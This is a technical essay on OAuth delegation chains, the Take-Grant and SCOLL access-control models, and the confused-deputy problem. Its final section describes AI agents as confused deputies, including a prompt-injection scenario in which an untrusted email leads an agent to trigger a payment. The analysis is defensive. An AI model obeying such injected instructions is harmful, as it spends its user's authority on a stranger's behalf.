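### The actor claim in OAuth

Many web services control access with OAuth, a family of standards in which an authorization server issues tokens that applications present instead of a user's password. Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define how a service that has received one token can trade it for another to call the next service. This standard, also known as RFC 8693, allows the new token to record the chain. If a user named Priya asked the coding agent for a change, the subagent's token might include:

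```json
{
  "sub": "priya",
  "aud": "repository",
  "act": {
    "sub": "test-subagent",
    "act": { "sub": "coding-agent" }
  }
}
```

The outer `sub` is the user the request is made for, and `aud` is the service that should accept the token. The first `act`, short for actor, identifies the current actor, and the `act` nested inside it identifies the previous one. A longer chain would have more nested `act` levels.

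The repository can use this to refuse the subagent and still accept the coding agent, so OAuth also supports revocation by party. But Jones and colleagues allow a service to consider only the outer claims and the current actor when it makes its decision. Earlier actors are "informational only". If the company bans the coding agent, the repository is not allowed to refuse the subagent's token merely because it lists the coding agent as an earlier actor.

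The authorization server can also omit the actor from the token, which the standard calls impersonation. The token then identifies only Priya, so the repository cannot distinguish the subagent's requests from hers.

When the claim is present, it proves that the authorization server vouched for the chain, but not that the coding agent took part. In Horton, Carol has more direct evidence of the introduction, because the request to admit Bob arrives through the stub she made for Alice. The repository, by contrast, has to trust the server, which may have received misleading information. The standard requires the server to check that the user's token and the actor's token are each valid, but not that both belong to the same task. A compromised agent with tokens from two tasks might therefore obtain a signed record of a delegation that never happened. The optional `may_act` claim reduces this risk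 by listing who may act for the user.

As with Horton's stubs, revoking the original access does not necessarily end the access derived from it. Jones and colleagues note that an exchange creates no tight link between the old token and the new one, and they let each system decide whether revoking the old token also revokes the new one. Tokens usually limit the damage by expiring, and the one in the standard's main example lasts a minute.

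### Proposals for agent delegation records

Several 2026 drafts try to make the delegation chain in a token more trustworthy. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) proposes a common way to represent actors, including AI agents, across different kinds of token. Two companion drafts add signatures.

In McGuinness's *OAuth Actor Receipts for Delegation Provenance* (2026), each authorization server that adds an actor also signs a receipt. In one example from an earlier version, a company's server signs a receipt for a travel assistant, and a travel provider's server later signs one for a booking tool. The second receipt includes a hash of the first, a short value calculated from its exact text, so any change to the first can be detected. An airline that receives the token can check each step against the server that recorded it.

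Receipts prove that particular servers vouched for particular actors. The travel provider's server could not forge the company's receipt. But a server could still sign a false receipt for a step it adds itself, and the receipts do not show what each earlier token permitted. Receipts add little within a single company, where one server usually signs everything.

*OAuth Actor-Signed Hop Proofs* (McGuinness, 2026) has the actors sign as well. Before the travel provider's server issues a token for the booking tool, the tool signs a statement that identifies the tool, the user and the service the token is for. A dishonest server cannot forge this signature. The signature protects the airline only if the airline requires it, because a dishonest server could leave it out, and only if the airline gets the tool's public key from a source the server does not control.

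Even then, the proof shows only that someone used the tool's key to agree to the delegation. It doesn't establish intent or reveal whether the key was stolen or the actor colluded with the server. The actor signs before the token exists, so someone who has the proof might reuse it in a second token for the same user, actor and service until the proof expires. Each proof typically adds 400 to 800 bytes to the token. The signature also gives the actor less privacy than Horton's private logs do, because anyone who sees the token can prove to others that the actor took part.

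*Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) lets each system choose how much evidence to collect and how much to reveal. In a "declared" chain, services rely on the authorization server's account of who acted. In a "verified" chain, each actor signs its own step. The server stores the signed steps and puts only a short cryptographic summary of them in the token. This keeps tokens small, but an auditor can check the signatures only if the server has kept them. Either kind of chain can show a service all the actors, some of them or only the current one. To refuse requests because of an earlier actor, a service must use a version that reveals that actor.

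These records mostly concern the caller. In the 2025 discussion, Miller said that the service that answers the call, or whoever introduced the two, might also be at fault. Horton covers the service because Bob's proxy records Carol as responsible for the page. Prasad and colleagues come closest to this with an optional acknowledgment, in which the recipient of a request signs that it accepts responsibility for that step. The acknowledgment doesn't show that the recipient carried out the step properly.

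All of these are drafts that may still change or be abandoned. But a related document, *OAuth Identity and Authorization Chaining Across Domains* by Schwenkschuster, Kasselman and colleagues (2026), was in the queue for publication as a proposed standard in August 2026.

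## Calculating what amplification makes reachable: Take-Grant and SCOLL

Delegation records help people assign responsibility after something goes wrong. Before a system runs, its designer may want to know whether a certain program could ever obtain a certain access, which researchers call the safety question. Sandhu (1991) points out in *Expressive Power of the Schematic Protection Model* that changes that each look innocent can together produce an undesirable result. For example, if one program passes on a sealed box and another passes on its unsealer, whoever receives both can open the box.

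Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman formalized the question in 1976. In their model, a table lists the rights that each subject, such as a user or a running program, has to every other subject and object. A command checks some cells for rights and, if it finds them, changes the table. Harrison and colleagues proved that no algorithm can answer the safety question for every set of commands, because commands can simulate any computer program. Sandhu notes that this remains true even if commands never delete anything and each checks only two cells. Unsealing needs at least two checks, one for the box and one for the unsealer.

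The 1976 result shows that some rules are undecidable, but Miller and Shapiro complain that people often misread it as showing that all rules are. Spiessens writes in *Patterns of Safe Collaboration* (2007) that Jones, Lipton and Snyder also presented a system in 1976 for which a computer can find the answer quickly. That system developed into the Take-Grant model.

### Four rules for changing a graph

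Take-Grant represents a system as a graph. Its vertices are subjects, which can act, and objects, which cannot. An arrow from *x* to *y* carries labels for the rights that *x* has to *y*, such as *r* for read, *w* for write, *t* for take and *g* for grant. Objects can have rights too, as a directory does, but only subjects can apply the four rules:

- **Take:** if *x* has *t* to *y*, and *y* has some right to *z*, then *x* can copy that right for itself.
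- **Grant:** if *x* has *g* to *y*, and *x* has some right to *z*, then *x* can give *y* a copy of that right.
- **Create:** *x* can create a new vertex and receive any rights to it.
- **Remove:** *x* can give up any of its rights.

An analyst can ignore the last rule, because no rule depends on a right being absent.

Rights can also travel against the direction of an arrow if there is a subject at each end. Suppose Alice has *g* to Bob, so she can give him rights but cannot take any. Bob can read a file, and they both want Alice to be able to read it:

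1. Alice creates a new vertex *v*, with *t* and *g* to it.
2. Alice grants Bob *g* to *v*.
3. Bob grants *v* the right to read the file.
4. Alice takes that right from *v*.

The new vertex works like a return address. A similar method lets Alice give Bob something if she has *t* to him. Two cooperating subjects can therefore share everything they have if either has *t* or *g* to the other.

### The can-share question

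The predicate can-share(*α*, *x*, *y*, *G*₀) is true if *x* can eventually get the right *α* to *y*, starting from the graph *G*₀. This depends on two kinds of connection. An island is a largest possible group of subjects that *t* and *g* arrows connect directly, in either direction. Everyone on an island can get any right that anyone else there has. A bridge is a path, possibly through objects, along which two subjects can pass rights. For example, if one subject has *g* to a shared folder and another has *t* to it, the folder is part of a bridge. If both have only *t*, the folder doesn't connect them, because neither can put a right in it for the other to take.

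Bishop (1988), in *The Sharing of Rights and Information in a Capability-Based Protection System*, gives the exact conditions. Unless *x* already has the right, all four of these must hold:

1. Some vertex *s* has the right *α* to *y*.
2. Some subject *s*′ either is *s* or can reach *s* through a chain of *t* arrows, and so take the right from it.
3. Some subject *x*′ either is *x* or can reach *x* through a chain of *t* arrows that ends with one *g* arrow, and so give the right to it.
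4. A series of islands and bridges connects *s*′ to *x*′.

A computer can check these conditions in time proportional to the size of the initial graph. Lipton and Snyder (1977) published an early algorithm of this kind in *A linear time algorithm for deciding subject security*. The calculation still works when subjects can create any number of new vertices because, as Spiessens explains, one new subject for each original one is enough for rights to spread as far as they ever can.

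### From rights to information

A program that never gets the right to read a file may still get a copy of the text. In 1979, Bishop and Snyder extended Take-Grant with "de facto" rules, which add a dashed arrow from *x* to *z* when information could flow from *z* to *x*:

| Rule | When information can reach *x* from *z* |
|---|---|
| Post | *x* can read *y*, and *z* can write to *y* |
| Pass | *y* can read *z* and write to *x* |
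| Spy | *x* can read *y*, and *y* can read *z* |
| Find | *z* can write to *y*, and *y* can write to *x* |

Only a subject can do the reading or writing. A dashed arrow is not a right, so nobody can take or grant it. Miller and Shapiro adapted their distinction between permission and authority from this work.

The extended model makes it very hard to keep two parts of a system separate. Spiessens observes that separation requires every path between them to contain at least two objects in a row, because two programs can communicate through a single shared file.

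### Why the basic rules miss a sealed box

None of these rules describes unsealing. An analyst could draw a box as an object with an arrow to its contents, but would then have to decide who has *t* to the box:

- If everyone who holds the box has *t* to it, a clerk who merely carries the box can open it.
- If nobody has *t* to the box, nobody can open it, even with the unsealer. This is the more dangerous mistake, because the analysis misses access that exists.
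- If the unsealer is an object that has *t* to every box from its pair, anyone who can take from the unsealer can open all of those boxes, including ones they have never received. This describes Redell's manager with its table of full-strength capabilities better than it describes an unsealer.

An arrow relates two vertices, but unsealing depends on a subject, an unsealer and a box. Spiessens notes a similar problem with describing who will send what to whom. He adds that one can always translate such three-way relations into two-way ones, but that this makes the model more complicated.

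For a single box, two new labels are enough. Let *h* from *x* to *b* mean that *x* holds the box *b*, and let *u* from *x* to *b* mean that *x* holds the unsealer that opens *b*. The amplification rule is then:

> If *x* has both *h* and *u* to *b*, and *b* has the right *α* to *z*, then *x* gains *α* to *z*.

This is the take rule with a pair of labels in place of *t*. The two labels can reach *x* by different routes, and *x* needs both to open the box.

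### Four vertices worked by hand

Consider the payroll program that seals a salary record and leaves the box with a clerk. The graph has two subjects, Clerk and Payroll, and two objects, Box and Record. It starts with four arrows:

- Clerk has *h* to Box.
- Clerk has *g* to Payroll, so the clerk can submit things to the program.
- Payroll has *u* to Box.
- Box has *r* to Record.

The first analysis uses only the take and grant rules. Nobody has *t* to anything, so take never applies. Clerk can grant Payroll *h* to Box. After that, no rule adds anything new, so the graph has reached a fixed point. Payroll now holds both the box and its unsealer, but only Box has an arrow to Record. The can-share conditions give the same answer, because no subject can reach Box through *t* arrows. The result is therefore that no program can read the record, which is wrong.

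With the amplification rule added, Clerk grants Payroll *h* to Box as before. Payroll then has *h* and *u* to Box, so it gains *r* to Record. It has no *t* or *g*, so it cannot pass this right on, and the graph is again at a fixed point. Payroll can read the record and Clerk cannot, which is the correct result.

But this leaves out the create rule. Under that rule, Clerk can make a return address and grant Payroll *g* to it. Payroll can then put the right to read the record there for Clerk to take. Payroll can also put the unsealer there, which would let Clerk open the box directly.

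| | Start | Take and grant | With unsealing | With unsealing and creation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Payroll holds the box | no | yes | yes | yes |
| Payroll can read the record | no | no | yes | yes |
| Clerk has the unsealer | no | no | no | yes |
| Clerk can read the record | no | no | no | yes |

The last column is a false alarm if Payroll's code never gives away records or unsealers. Take-Grant assumes that every subject will use all its rights to help every other subject, but a service that amplifies rights is useful only if it restricts how it uses its rights for others.

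The amplification rule can also slow the calculation. The linear-time method looks for single paths, but amplification requires two separate paths to meet at the same subject. An analyst can handle this by repeatedly using can-share to check whether any subject can get both *h* and *u* to a box, and adding a *t* arrow from each subject that can to that box. The number of subject-box pairs is finite, so the process must end, but it may take many passes. Sealing new boxes makes no difference in this worst-case analysis, because a subject willing to pass on a box could pass on the contents instead.

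### Links that need two tickets

An earlier model can express the amplification rule without special labels for each box. Sandhu, in *The Schematic Protection Model*, gives every subject and object a permanent type. A capability is a ticket such as *B*/*h*, which gives its holder the right *h* to *B*. A subject can copy a ticket to another subject only if three conditions hold:

- The ticket carries a copy flag.
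- There is a link from the source to the destination.
- A filter for that link allows this type of ticket to pass between subjects of these types.

The formula for a link can require several tickets. In one of Sandhu's examples, a link from *X* to *Y* exists only if *X* has a "send" ticket for *Y* and *Y* has a "receive" ticket for *X*.

Sandhu's own examples include departments that share documents, but the model can also describe the payroll box. A passive thing that holds rights counts as a subject in this model, so the box can be the source of a link. If dom(*P*) is the set of tickets that the payroll program *P* holds, the link from box *B* to *P* is

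link(*B*, *P*) = *B*/*h* ∈ dom(*P*) ∧ *B*/*u* ∈ dom(*P*).

The program gets *B*/*h* from the clerk. It gets *B*/*u* through an operation called demand, which lets every subject of one type obtain a specified ticket for any entity of another type. If programs of type "payroll" may demand *u* for anything of type "salary box", the rule also covers future boxes, and the type serves as a brand. The filter can let the program receive a read ticket for the record that has no copy flag. The program then cannot pass the ticket to the clerk, so this version avoids the false alarm.

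It has two limitations. An administrator fixes the types when setting up the system, whereas a program that calls Morris's Createseal gets a new brand while it runs. And withholding the copy flag doesn't stop the payroll program from passing the record's contents to the clerk.

Sandhu analyses such a system by assuming that all subjects cooperate and calculating the most they could obtain. UC Davis' lecture slides *ECS 235B, Foundations of Computer and Information Security* (2026) call the result a maximal state, in which further entries and rights no longer affect the analysis.

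The calculation is certain to finish only if the scheme limits how subjects create other subjects. Sandhu allows an ordinary user to create a more powerful subject, such as a system manager for experiments, but that manager must not be able to create ordinary users. A subject can create others of its own type only if they are no more powerful than it is. Sandhu conjectured that most practical schemes would satisfy these limits.

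### How trusted behavior removes false alarms

Sandhu acknowledged that some analyses have to make assumptions about particular subjects. A Unix superuser can change almost any permission, so an analysis in which the superuser helps everyone would be useless. Harrison and colleagues had suggested deleting trusted subjects from the model. Spiessens objects that this is all or nothing. In the payroll example, deletion would remove the false alarm about the clerk, but also the only program that is supposed to open the box.

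Miller and Shapiro describe the choice in terms of bounds. An analyst who looks only at which programs hold which capabilities can answer "no" or "maybe" to whether a program will get some access. Also considering some programs' code lets the analyst change some of the "maybe" answers to a reliable "no".

Ignoring how programs behave had led researchers to mistaken conclusions about capabilities. Spiessens discusses Earl Boebert's 1984 proof that unmodified capability systems cannot stop secret information from flowing to users with a lower clearance. He infers that Boebert assumed anyone who could write to an object could also pass it any capability they held. A grant right works that way in Take-Grant, but a programmer can write a program that accepts data in messages and refuses capabilities.

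SCOLL (Safe Collaboration Language) lets an analyst state what each trusted program will and will not do. Researchers at the Université catholique de Louvain developed it from the model in Spiessens and Van Roy's *A Practical Formal Model for Safety Analysis in Capability-Based Systems*. *SCOLL* (Jaradin, Spiessens and Van Roy, 2005) starts from the observation that a capability passes only when one party offers it and another accepts it. Each party does so only if its code allows.

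In simplified notation, the main rules are the first two below. Jaradin and colleagues listed sealer-unsealer pairs as a pattern they had still to analyse, and the third rule is one way to add them:

```
send:    holds(S,T)  holds(S,X)  offers(S,T,X)  accepts(T)     =>  holds(T,X)
fetch:   holds(S,T)  holds(T,X)  asks(S,T)      returns(T,X)   =>  holds(S,X)
unseal:  holds(S,U)  holds(S,B)  opens(U,B)     contains(B,X)  =>  holds(S,X)
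```

The facts about who offers, accepts, asks and returns come from the declared behavior of each subject. The analyst declares that an untrusted program does everything it can. SCOLL then applies the rules until they produce no new facts. This process must end because SCOLL never withdraws a fact and the number of possible facts is finite. Spiessens puts that number at the order of *s*ᵃ, where *s* is the number of subjects and *a* is the largest number of subjects in one fact. With five subjects and three subjects per fact, there are at most 125 facts of each kind.

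### The payroll program in SCOLL

The payroll example now has five subjects, because the unsealer is separate from the program that holds it. At the start, the clerk holds the payroll program and the box, the program holds the unsealer, the unsealer opens the box, and the box contains the record. The clerk is untrusted. The analyst declares only one thing about the payroll program, that it accepts what others send.

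1. The clerk offers the box to the program, which accepts it. The send rule gives holds(payroll, box).
2. The program now holds the box and its unsealer. The unseal rule gives holds(payroll, record).
3. The clerk asks the program for the record. The fetch rule does not apply, because the program does not return it.

The clerk can also send the program a reference to itself, but gains nothing by doing so because the program offers nothing to anyone. No rule gives the clerk the record, so the analysis no longer raises the false alarm. If the analyst instead treats the payroll program as untrusted, the program returns whatever it holds, and the clerk obtains both the record and the unsealer.

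SCOLL can also work backwards from a requirement to the behavior that would satisfy it. Here, the payroll program must never give the clerk the record or the unsealer, but it can safely return the box. An author who thought only the record was secret could easily forget to withhold the unsealer.

Jaradin and colleagues ran this kind of search on a pattern for revocable access. Alice wants to let Bob use Carol temporarily, so she gives him a caretaker, an intermediary that forwards his requests until she switches it off. This works only if Bob never gets a direct reference to Carol. The tool searched for the most cooperative behavior Carol could have without breaking that condition, and found two solutions. In both, Carol must not give a reference to herself to Bob or to Dave, an untrusted object Bob can reach through her. One solution also forbids her from giving herself to Alice, and the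 other forbids her from giving Alice to Bob or Dave. If she did both, Alice could pass Carol on to Bob, because Alice does not check what she passes on.

#### Modelling a deputy

Type managers are deputies because they use their own authority on behalf of clients. Spiessens divides the authority for a task into a part the client controls and a part the deputy controls. The client should supply its part by passing capabilities with the request, and the deputy should never use its own authority in place of the client's. Only the deputy's code can ensure this, since the intended use of each capability isn't known outside the deputy.

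In SCOLL, the difference between a careless deputy *D* and a careful one can come down to a single condition:

```
careless:  holds(D,X)     =>  writes(D,X)
careful:   received(D,X)  =>  writes(D,X)
```

Suppose the deputy also has a private file. The careless rule allows it to write a client's output there, while the careful rule allows this only if some client has sent it that file. The result is still an over-estimate, because once one client has legitimately sent a file, that fact stays true and the model allows the deputy to write there for any client. SCOLL can reduce this problem by making a response depend on what arrived in the same request.

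### What a SCOLL answer assumes

Jaradin and colleagues thought an exact calculation was impossible in general, because programs can keep creating new objects forever. SCOLL therefore lets one subject in the model stand for many real ones, such as a program and everything it creates. The combined subject must do anything any of its members would do. Jaradin and colleagues prove that if access is impossible in the simplified model, it is also impossible in the detailed one. But access that is possible in the simplified model may be impossible in the detailed one. For example, if an analyst merges the boxes from two sealer-unsealer pairs, either unsealer will appear to open all of them.

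This theorem relates one model to another, so it does not guarantee that the declarations match the code. An analyst who overlooks a debugging command that returns unsealed records will get a wrong "no" without any warning. The declarations should therefore allow anything the code might do.

The 2005 version also tracked capabilities but not data. It could show that the clerk never gets a reference to the record, but not that the payroll program never includes the salary in a reply. Jaradin and colleagues show that two clients could signal to each other through a supposedly one-way component by influencing whether it accepts messages, and that the analysis would not detect this.

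The unseal rule also leaves out timing. It treats opening a box as a single step that always works correctly, so a model with only this rule would not reveal the attack on the till in the JavaScript mint, which depends on one unsealing interrupting another.

### Proofs about the code of a sealer

A proof about the code can justify treating unsealing as one step. Swasey and colleagues give such a proof for a sealer-unsealer pair written in a small language with functions, changeable variables and multiple threads. Their program looks boxes up in a private table, as the JavaScript WeakMap version does, and a lock prevents two calls from using the table at once.

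The specification attaches to each pair a condition *φ*, which corresponds to the property in Morris's invariant rule. For intervals, *φ* requires that the smaller number come first. A call to `unseal` on any value, including an attacker's forgery, either gets stuck or returns a value that satisfies *φ*. The condition must be permanent, so it cannot depend on data that somebody else can still change.

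According to Swasey and colleagues, a module can publish one half of the pair if that half is "low", meaning that no code can use it to get a direct reference to the module's private memory.

- A module can publish `seal` if every low value satisfies *φ*, since an attacker can seal any low value.
- It can publish `unseal` if every value that satisfies *φ* is low, since an attacker can open any box.

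The interval module could safely publish `unseal`, because a pair of numbers gives access to nothing, but not `seal`, because other code could then seal invalid intervals such as (7, 3).

Their main theorem, that an attacker who receives only low values cannot make a verified program's assertions fail, rests on three assumptions about the attacker and the language. (An assertion is a statement in the code that some fact is true at that point, such as that an interval's minimum is no greater than its maximum.)

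- The attacker's code does not begin with any memory addresses in it. It can only use memory that it creates or that the verified program gives it.
- The attacker's code contains no assertions, because an attacker could easily write a false one.
- The language prevents programs from forging references or looking inside functions.

The proof assistant Coq checked the whole argument, so readers do not have to take each step on trust. The result covers correctness but not secrecy or availability. Every ordinary number counts as low, so a payroll program could publish a salary without violating the theorem. The theorem also allows an attacker to make a call get stuck. Sumii and Pierce's method, which tests whether outside code can tell two modules apart, suits secrecy better.

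### Proofs for capability processors

Machine code does not satisfy the third assumption on an ordinary processor, because a program can turn any integer into an address. On a capability processor such as CHERI, hardware checks replace the language's rules. In Cerisier, the 2026 logic for such processors, the condition on each seal number has the same role as *φ* and limits sharing in the same way. If untrusted code gets the authority to seal under a number, the condition must hold for everything that code could seal.

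A proof about a modelled processor applies to a real chip only if the chip enforces the same rules, including the ones that stop programs from forging capabilities. *Reasoning about External Calls* requires that no unsealer leaks. A graph calculation like the one for the clerk can check this across a whole system, provided that each trusted program's declared behavior covers everything its code can do.

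## Accidental amplification: the compiler's billing file and AI agents

The careless deputy in the SCOLL rules writes to any file that its own authority allows, no matter who chose the file. A compiler at Tymshare did this in about 1977 and wiped out billing information. Norm Hardy described the incident in a 1988 paper that named the problem the "confused deputy". Before the incident, he had thought capabilities were neat and tidy, and it convinced him that they were necessary.

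### How the compiler overwrote the billing file

In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy calls his account "nearly true" because he changed inessential details. Tymshare's operating system protected files much as Unix does. The compiler was in the system directory SYSX, and anyone who ran it could name a file to receive optional debugging output. The compiler also counted people's use of language features and wrote the totals to the file (SYSX)STAT.

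To let the compiler update this file, Tymshare gave it a privilege called "home files license", which allowed a program to write to any file in its own directory. The billing information was in the same directory, in (SYSX)BILL. The accident then took four steps:

1. A user who had come to know the name (SYSX)BILL gave it as the file for debugging output.
2. The compiler asked the operating system to open that file for writing.
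3. The operating system saw that the compiler had home files license, and agreed.
4. The compiler wrote debugging output over the billing information.

The compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the license. It was supposed to use the user's authority for debugging output and the license for statistics, but a request to open a file contained only a name, so the system allowed any write that either source permitted. The compiler needed a way to specify which authority to use for each request.

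Ambient authority is authority that applies to a request because of who is running, without the request specifying which authority to use. *Confused Deputy*, a discussion on Fission's forum, identifies two essential points in Hardy's case. The name the user gave for the file did not carry the authority to write to it, and the system implicitly applied the compiler's own permission. The name need not be a string of characters. One participant gives the example of a symbolic link, a file that points to another file. A user puts a link in a directory they control and asks a file server to read it. The server then uses its own permissions to follow the link to a file the user could not open.

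Web browsers have the same fault, according to Waterken, a project on secure web software. A browser uses the user's passwords but also takes instructions from the pages it displays, and a request to a bank's website doesn't show whether it came from the user or a page.

### Why Tymshare could not just add a check

Hardy considers the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse to write outside the user's directory, but people had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse to write to SYSX, but the directory did not have that name when the programmer wrote the code, and someone with proper access might want output there. It could refuse to write to (SYSX)BILL by name, but then someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared.

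The code for debugging output was correct until Tymshare granted the license. To foresee the problem, someone would have had to examine every place where the compiler wrote a file.

Tymshare added a system call that let a program "switch hats", so the compiler could ask to open the debugging file with the user's authority alone. The request for (SYSX)BILL would then fail. But some programs needed more than two hats, and the system had kinds of authority other than file access. The rules for opening a file also kept growing, and they contained fourteen ANDs and ORs when Hardy last wrote them down.

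### Passing a capability instead of a name

In a capability system, whoever installed the compiler would give it a capability for the statistics file. The user would supply a capability for the debugging file with each run. The compiler would write statistics through the first and debugging output through the second, without handling any file names.

A user who has no capability for the billing file then has nothing to pass. A billing clerk who has a capability for a file in SYSX can have the compiler write output there, which the check on directory names would have prevented. The statistics file is also safe, because knowing its name no longer helps anyone overwrite it. The Unix commands `cp` and `cat` differ in the same way.

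Hardy's fix also works for memory. CTSRD-CHERI's *Architectural rules for capability use* describes a program that passes a CHERI capability to the operating system kernel in a system call. The kernel may have access to all of memory through other capabilities, but if it uses only the one it received, the program cannot trick it into writing to someone else's memory. The hardware makes this possible but does not force the kernel's programmers to do it.

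### Four differences from designed amplification

The compiler and a Hydra type manager both combine a client's input with authority of their own. Here is the compiler beside Datafile-Append, the Hydra procedure that adds text to a file:

| | Tymshare's compiler | Datafile-Append |
|---|---|---|
| Source of the extra power | License attached to the program | Amplification template for one argument |
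| What the system checks | The file is in SYSX | The object is a Datafile and the caller may append to it |
| What the deputy gains | Writing to every file in SYSX, including later ones | Stated rights to one Datafile |
| Who can amplify | Programs with the license | Procedures with the template |

Some of these differences would not have saved the billing file. Tymshare could have listed every program with home files license, just as an auditor of Hydra could list the holders of a template. The list would have included the compiler, but nobody suspected it.

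A type check might not have helped either, because the debugging file and the billing file would both have passed if both were ordinary files. Stating the new rights limits the damage to the object the client designates, but here the client designated the billing file.

An explicit amplifying object gives more protection. Hydra's template applies to one argument of one procedure, so its author has to decide where the extra power goes, while the license applied to everything the compiler opened. A programmer could still have attached a template to the debugging argument by mistake. The decisive protection is that Hydra's caller must present a capability with the rights the template requires, and the user had no capability for the billing file.

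This also causes trouble for formal definitions. *Proof-of-Continuity* (2026), a paper on how authority spreads through distributed systems, defines a confused deputy by four conditions: a user lacks some privilege, a deputy has it, the user sends the deputy a request, and the deputy exercises the privilege as a consequence. Hardy's compiler meets all four, but so do the Unix `passwd` command and Datafile-Append, which adds capabilities to the Datafile's C-list at the request of a user who cannot add them. The definition covers every deputy that is useful for its privileges, and omits whether the resource's owner wanted the deputy to act for this user in this way.

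### Do capabilities cure the problem?

*Capability Myths Demolished* argues that capabilities are much better than access lists for avoiding confused deputies, partly because capabilities combine designation with authority, while access lists keep them separate.

In July 2026 Alan Karp, one of Horton's designers, asked other capability researchers for a proof that a capability system cannot contain a confused deputy. William Leslie replied in the thread, *Confused deputy* (Karp, 2026), that it can contain one. A deputy can put its own capabilities in a table and let clients choose one by name, which recreates Tymshare's directory inside a capability system. If the deputy instead uses a capability that the client provides, the client must already have had the authority.

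Mark Miller replied that a deputy is not vulnerable if it designates things only with capabilities. He called this a severe restriction that many normal deputies do not meet, although most of them are safe anyway. By his rule of thumb, a deputy that does not amplify rights is "probably not vulnerable". He added that the confused deputy attack "has nothing to do with confusing the deputy".

Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016), reach a more pessimistic conclusion. They define the problem for a small programming language in which an attacker's code runs alongside a deputy's. For each protected location, they ask two questions after the program has finished:

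- Would the location contain the same value whatever the attacker had done?
- Could the attacker have written that value there directly?

If the answer to both is no, the attacker has used the deputy to do something the attacker could not do alone. Rajani and colleagues then test four deputies in a capability version of their language:

| What the deputy does | What the attacker controls | Do capabilities stop it? |
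|---|---|---|
| Writes compiled code to a location the caller supplies | The location | Yes |
| Copies a value from the caller into a protected location | The value | No |
| Writes 41 or 42 to a protected location, depending on a yes-or-no value | The choice | No |
| Writes a value to a location that it looks up in memory, where someone has left a privileged capability | The value | No |

In the first case, an attacker who can supply a capability for a location could have written there directly, so the answer to the second question is yes. In the others, the deputy already has the capability it needs. Rajani and colleagues compare the second case to SQL injection, where an attacker gives a web server text that changes the commands the server sends to a database.

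Whether the last three are confused deputies depends on the definition. In the July thread, Karp described a confused deputy as one that "uses its permissions on a resource designated by somebody else". In the 41-or-42 example, the attacker designates nothing. Rajani and colleagues call it "implicit" designation, which stretches the word a good deal. Either way, an owner whose database now contains the attacker's text has a problem that capabilities alone do not solve.

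The broader definition, however, also covers legitimate behavior. If a compiler bills users according to the size of their programs, they can influence the billing file without being able to write to it, which counts as an attack. Rajani and colleagues therefore exclude code that a programmer has marked as "endorsed", meaning that it acts on someone else's behalf on purpose. Even the formal definition thus relies on a person to decide which influence is legitimate.

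They prove that capabilities prevent every attack of this kind if neither the deputy's unendorsed code nor the initial memory contains a capability for a protected location the attacker wants to change. They concede that this condition makes the language useless for almost all practical purposes. A type manager would violate it, because its job is to hold power that its clients lack.

They propose tracking where values come from instead. Each value carries a label for the least trusted source that influenced it, and the system blocks writes to any location more trusted than the value's label. A basic version follows values only as the program copies them. A full version also follows influence through decisions, as in the 41-or-42 example. It prevents all such attacks in their language without restricting the deputy's code, but takes more work at run time.

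The argument has continued on the mailing list *cap-talk*, where a 26-message thread about the paper ended in October 2026. Miller wrote in an earlier thread there, *Testing for a confused deputy vulnerability* (2019), that he knew of no automated system for spotting likely confused deputies.

### When the holder of an unsealer is the deputy

Miller's rule of thumb singles out amplification because a sealed box designates its contents without giving its holder the authority to use them, and the deputy supplies that authority. Designation without authority is also the first of the two essential points in the compiler case.

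Suppose the payroll program that seals salary records also emails payslips. Each request contains a sealed box and an address. A clerk who stores boxes for the whole office sends in a colleague's box with the clerk's own address. The seal correctly shows that the box is genuine, but it authenticates nothing else, so the program unseals the box and emails the colleague's salary to the clerk.

The same thing can happen with `token_unseal` in the CHERIoT Platform's operating system, because the types it compares do not identify the program that presented the handle. This is harmless if anyone who holds a handle is supposed to be entitled to everything the service offers, as with the JavaScript mint's purses.

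The payroll boxes are different because the clerk is supposed to carry them without reading them. The program could send payslips only to an address inside the sealed record, or require a second capability that only the employee has. CHERI's explicit unsealing would not help, because the program was meant to open the box.

### What changes when the deputy is an AI agent

An AI agent typically holds credentials for email, files or payments, and reads text that strangers wrote. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) lists three differences from Hardy's case. The agent's decisions depend on its prompt and are probabilistic. Its authority comes from a chain of people, programs and services instead of one operating system. And the attacker's request arrives inside a document, email or tool result, whereas the compiler's user had to make the request explicitly.

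It then traces a path from an inbox to a payment:

1. A user authorizes an agent to summarize the invoices in an inbox.
2. The agent reads a message from an untrusted sender.
3. The message contains text that asks for a payment.
4. The agent passes the request to a finance subagent, and leaves out the fact that its own task was read-only.
5. The payment tool receives a valid credential and makes the payment.

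The finance subagent's credential provided the authority to carry out the sender's instruction. The payment service can authenticate the caller, but it cannot detect that a stranger's email caused the call. Its log would look the same if the user had wanted the payment.

*Silent Egress* (2026), a study of agents that leak data, identifies a further difference. In the classic case it is unclear whom the deputy is serving, while with an agent it is unclear what the user intended, because the agent cannot reliably distinguish the user's request to fetch a page from instructions on that page. Hat-switching would not help much. The compiler already distinguished its debugging output and lacked only a way to indicate this, whereas an agent may use the user's authority to request the payment because it has mistaken the page's instructions for the user's.

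A person can also confuse an agent directly, without hidden text. In an example from *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026), an employee with no access to the personnel database asks an agent for everyone's salary. The agent, which has access for its administrative tasks, answers. The familiar remedy is to handle the request with the employee's permissions rather than the agent's.

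The problem may be worse between agents. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) argues that language models are particularly susceptible to it because developers generally do not train them to question the authority of whoever prompts them, so a subagent tends to treat another agent's request as legitimate. *DelegateGuard* (2026) proposes to attenuate authority each time one agent delegates to another. A trusted component turns the user's request into a grant that specifies purpose, operations and destinations, and each agent can pass on that grant or a narrower one. A monitor outside the model checks every upload, email and new delegation. In the invoice example, the read-only limit would then apply to the finance subagent whether or not the first agent mentioned it.

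Access control between agents is not enough to keep data private. *DelegateGuard* cites OMNI-LEAK, a study that found private data leaking between agents even with access control in place.

### A tool server that borrowed another server's access

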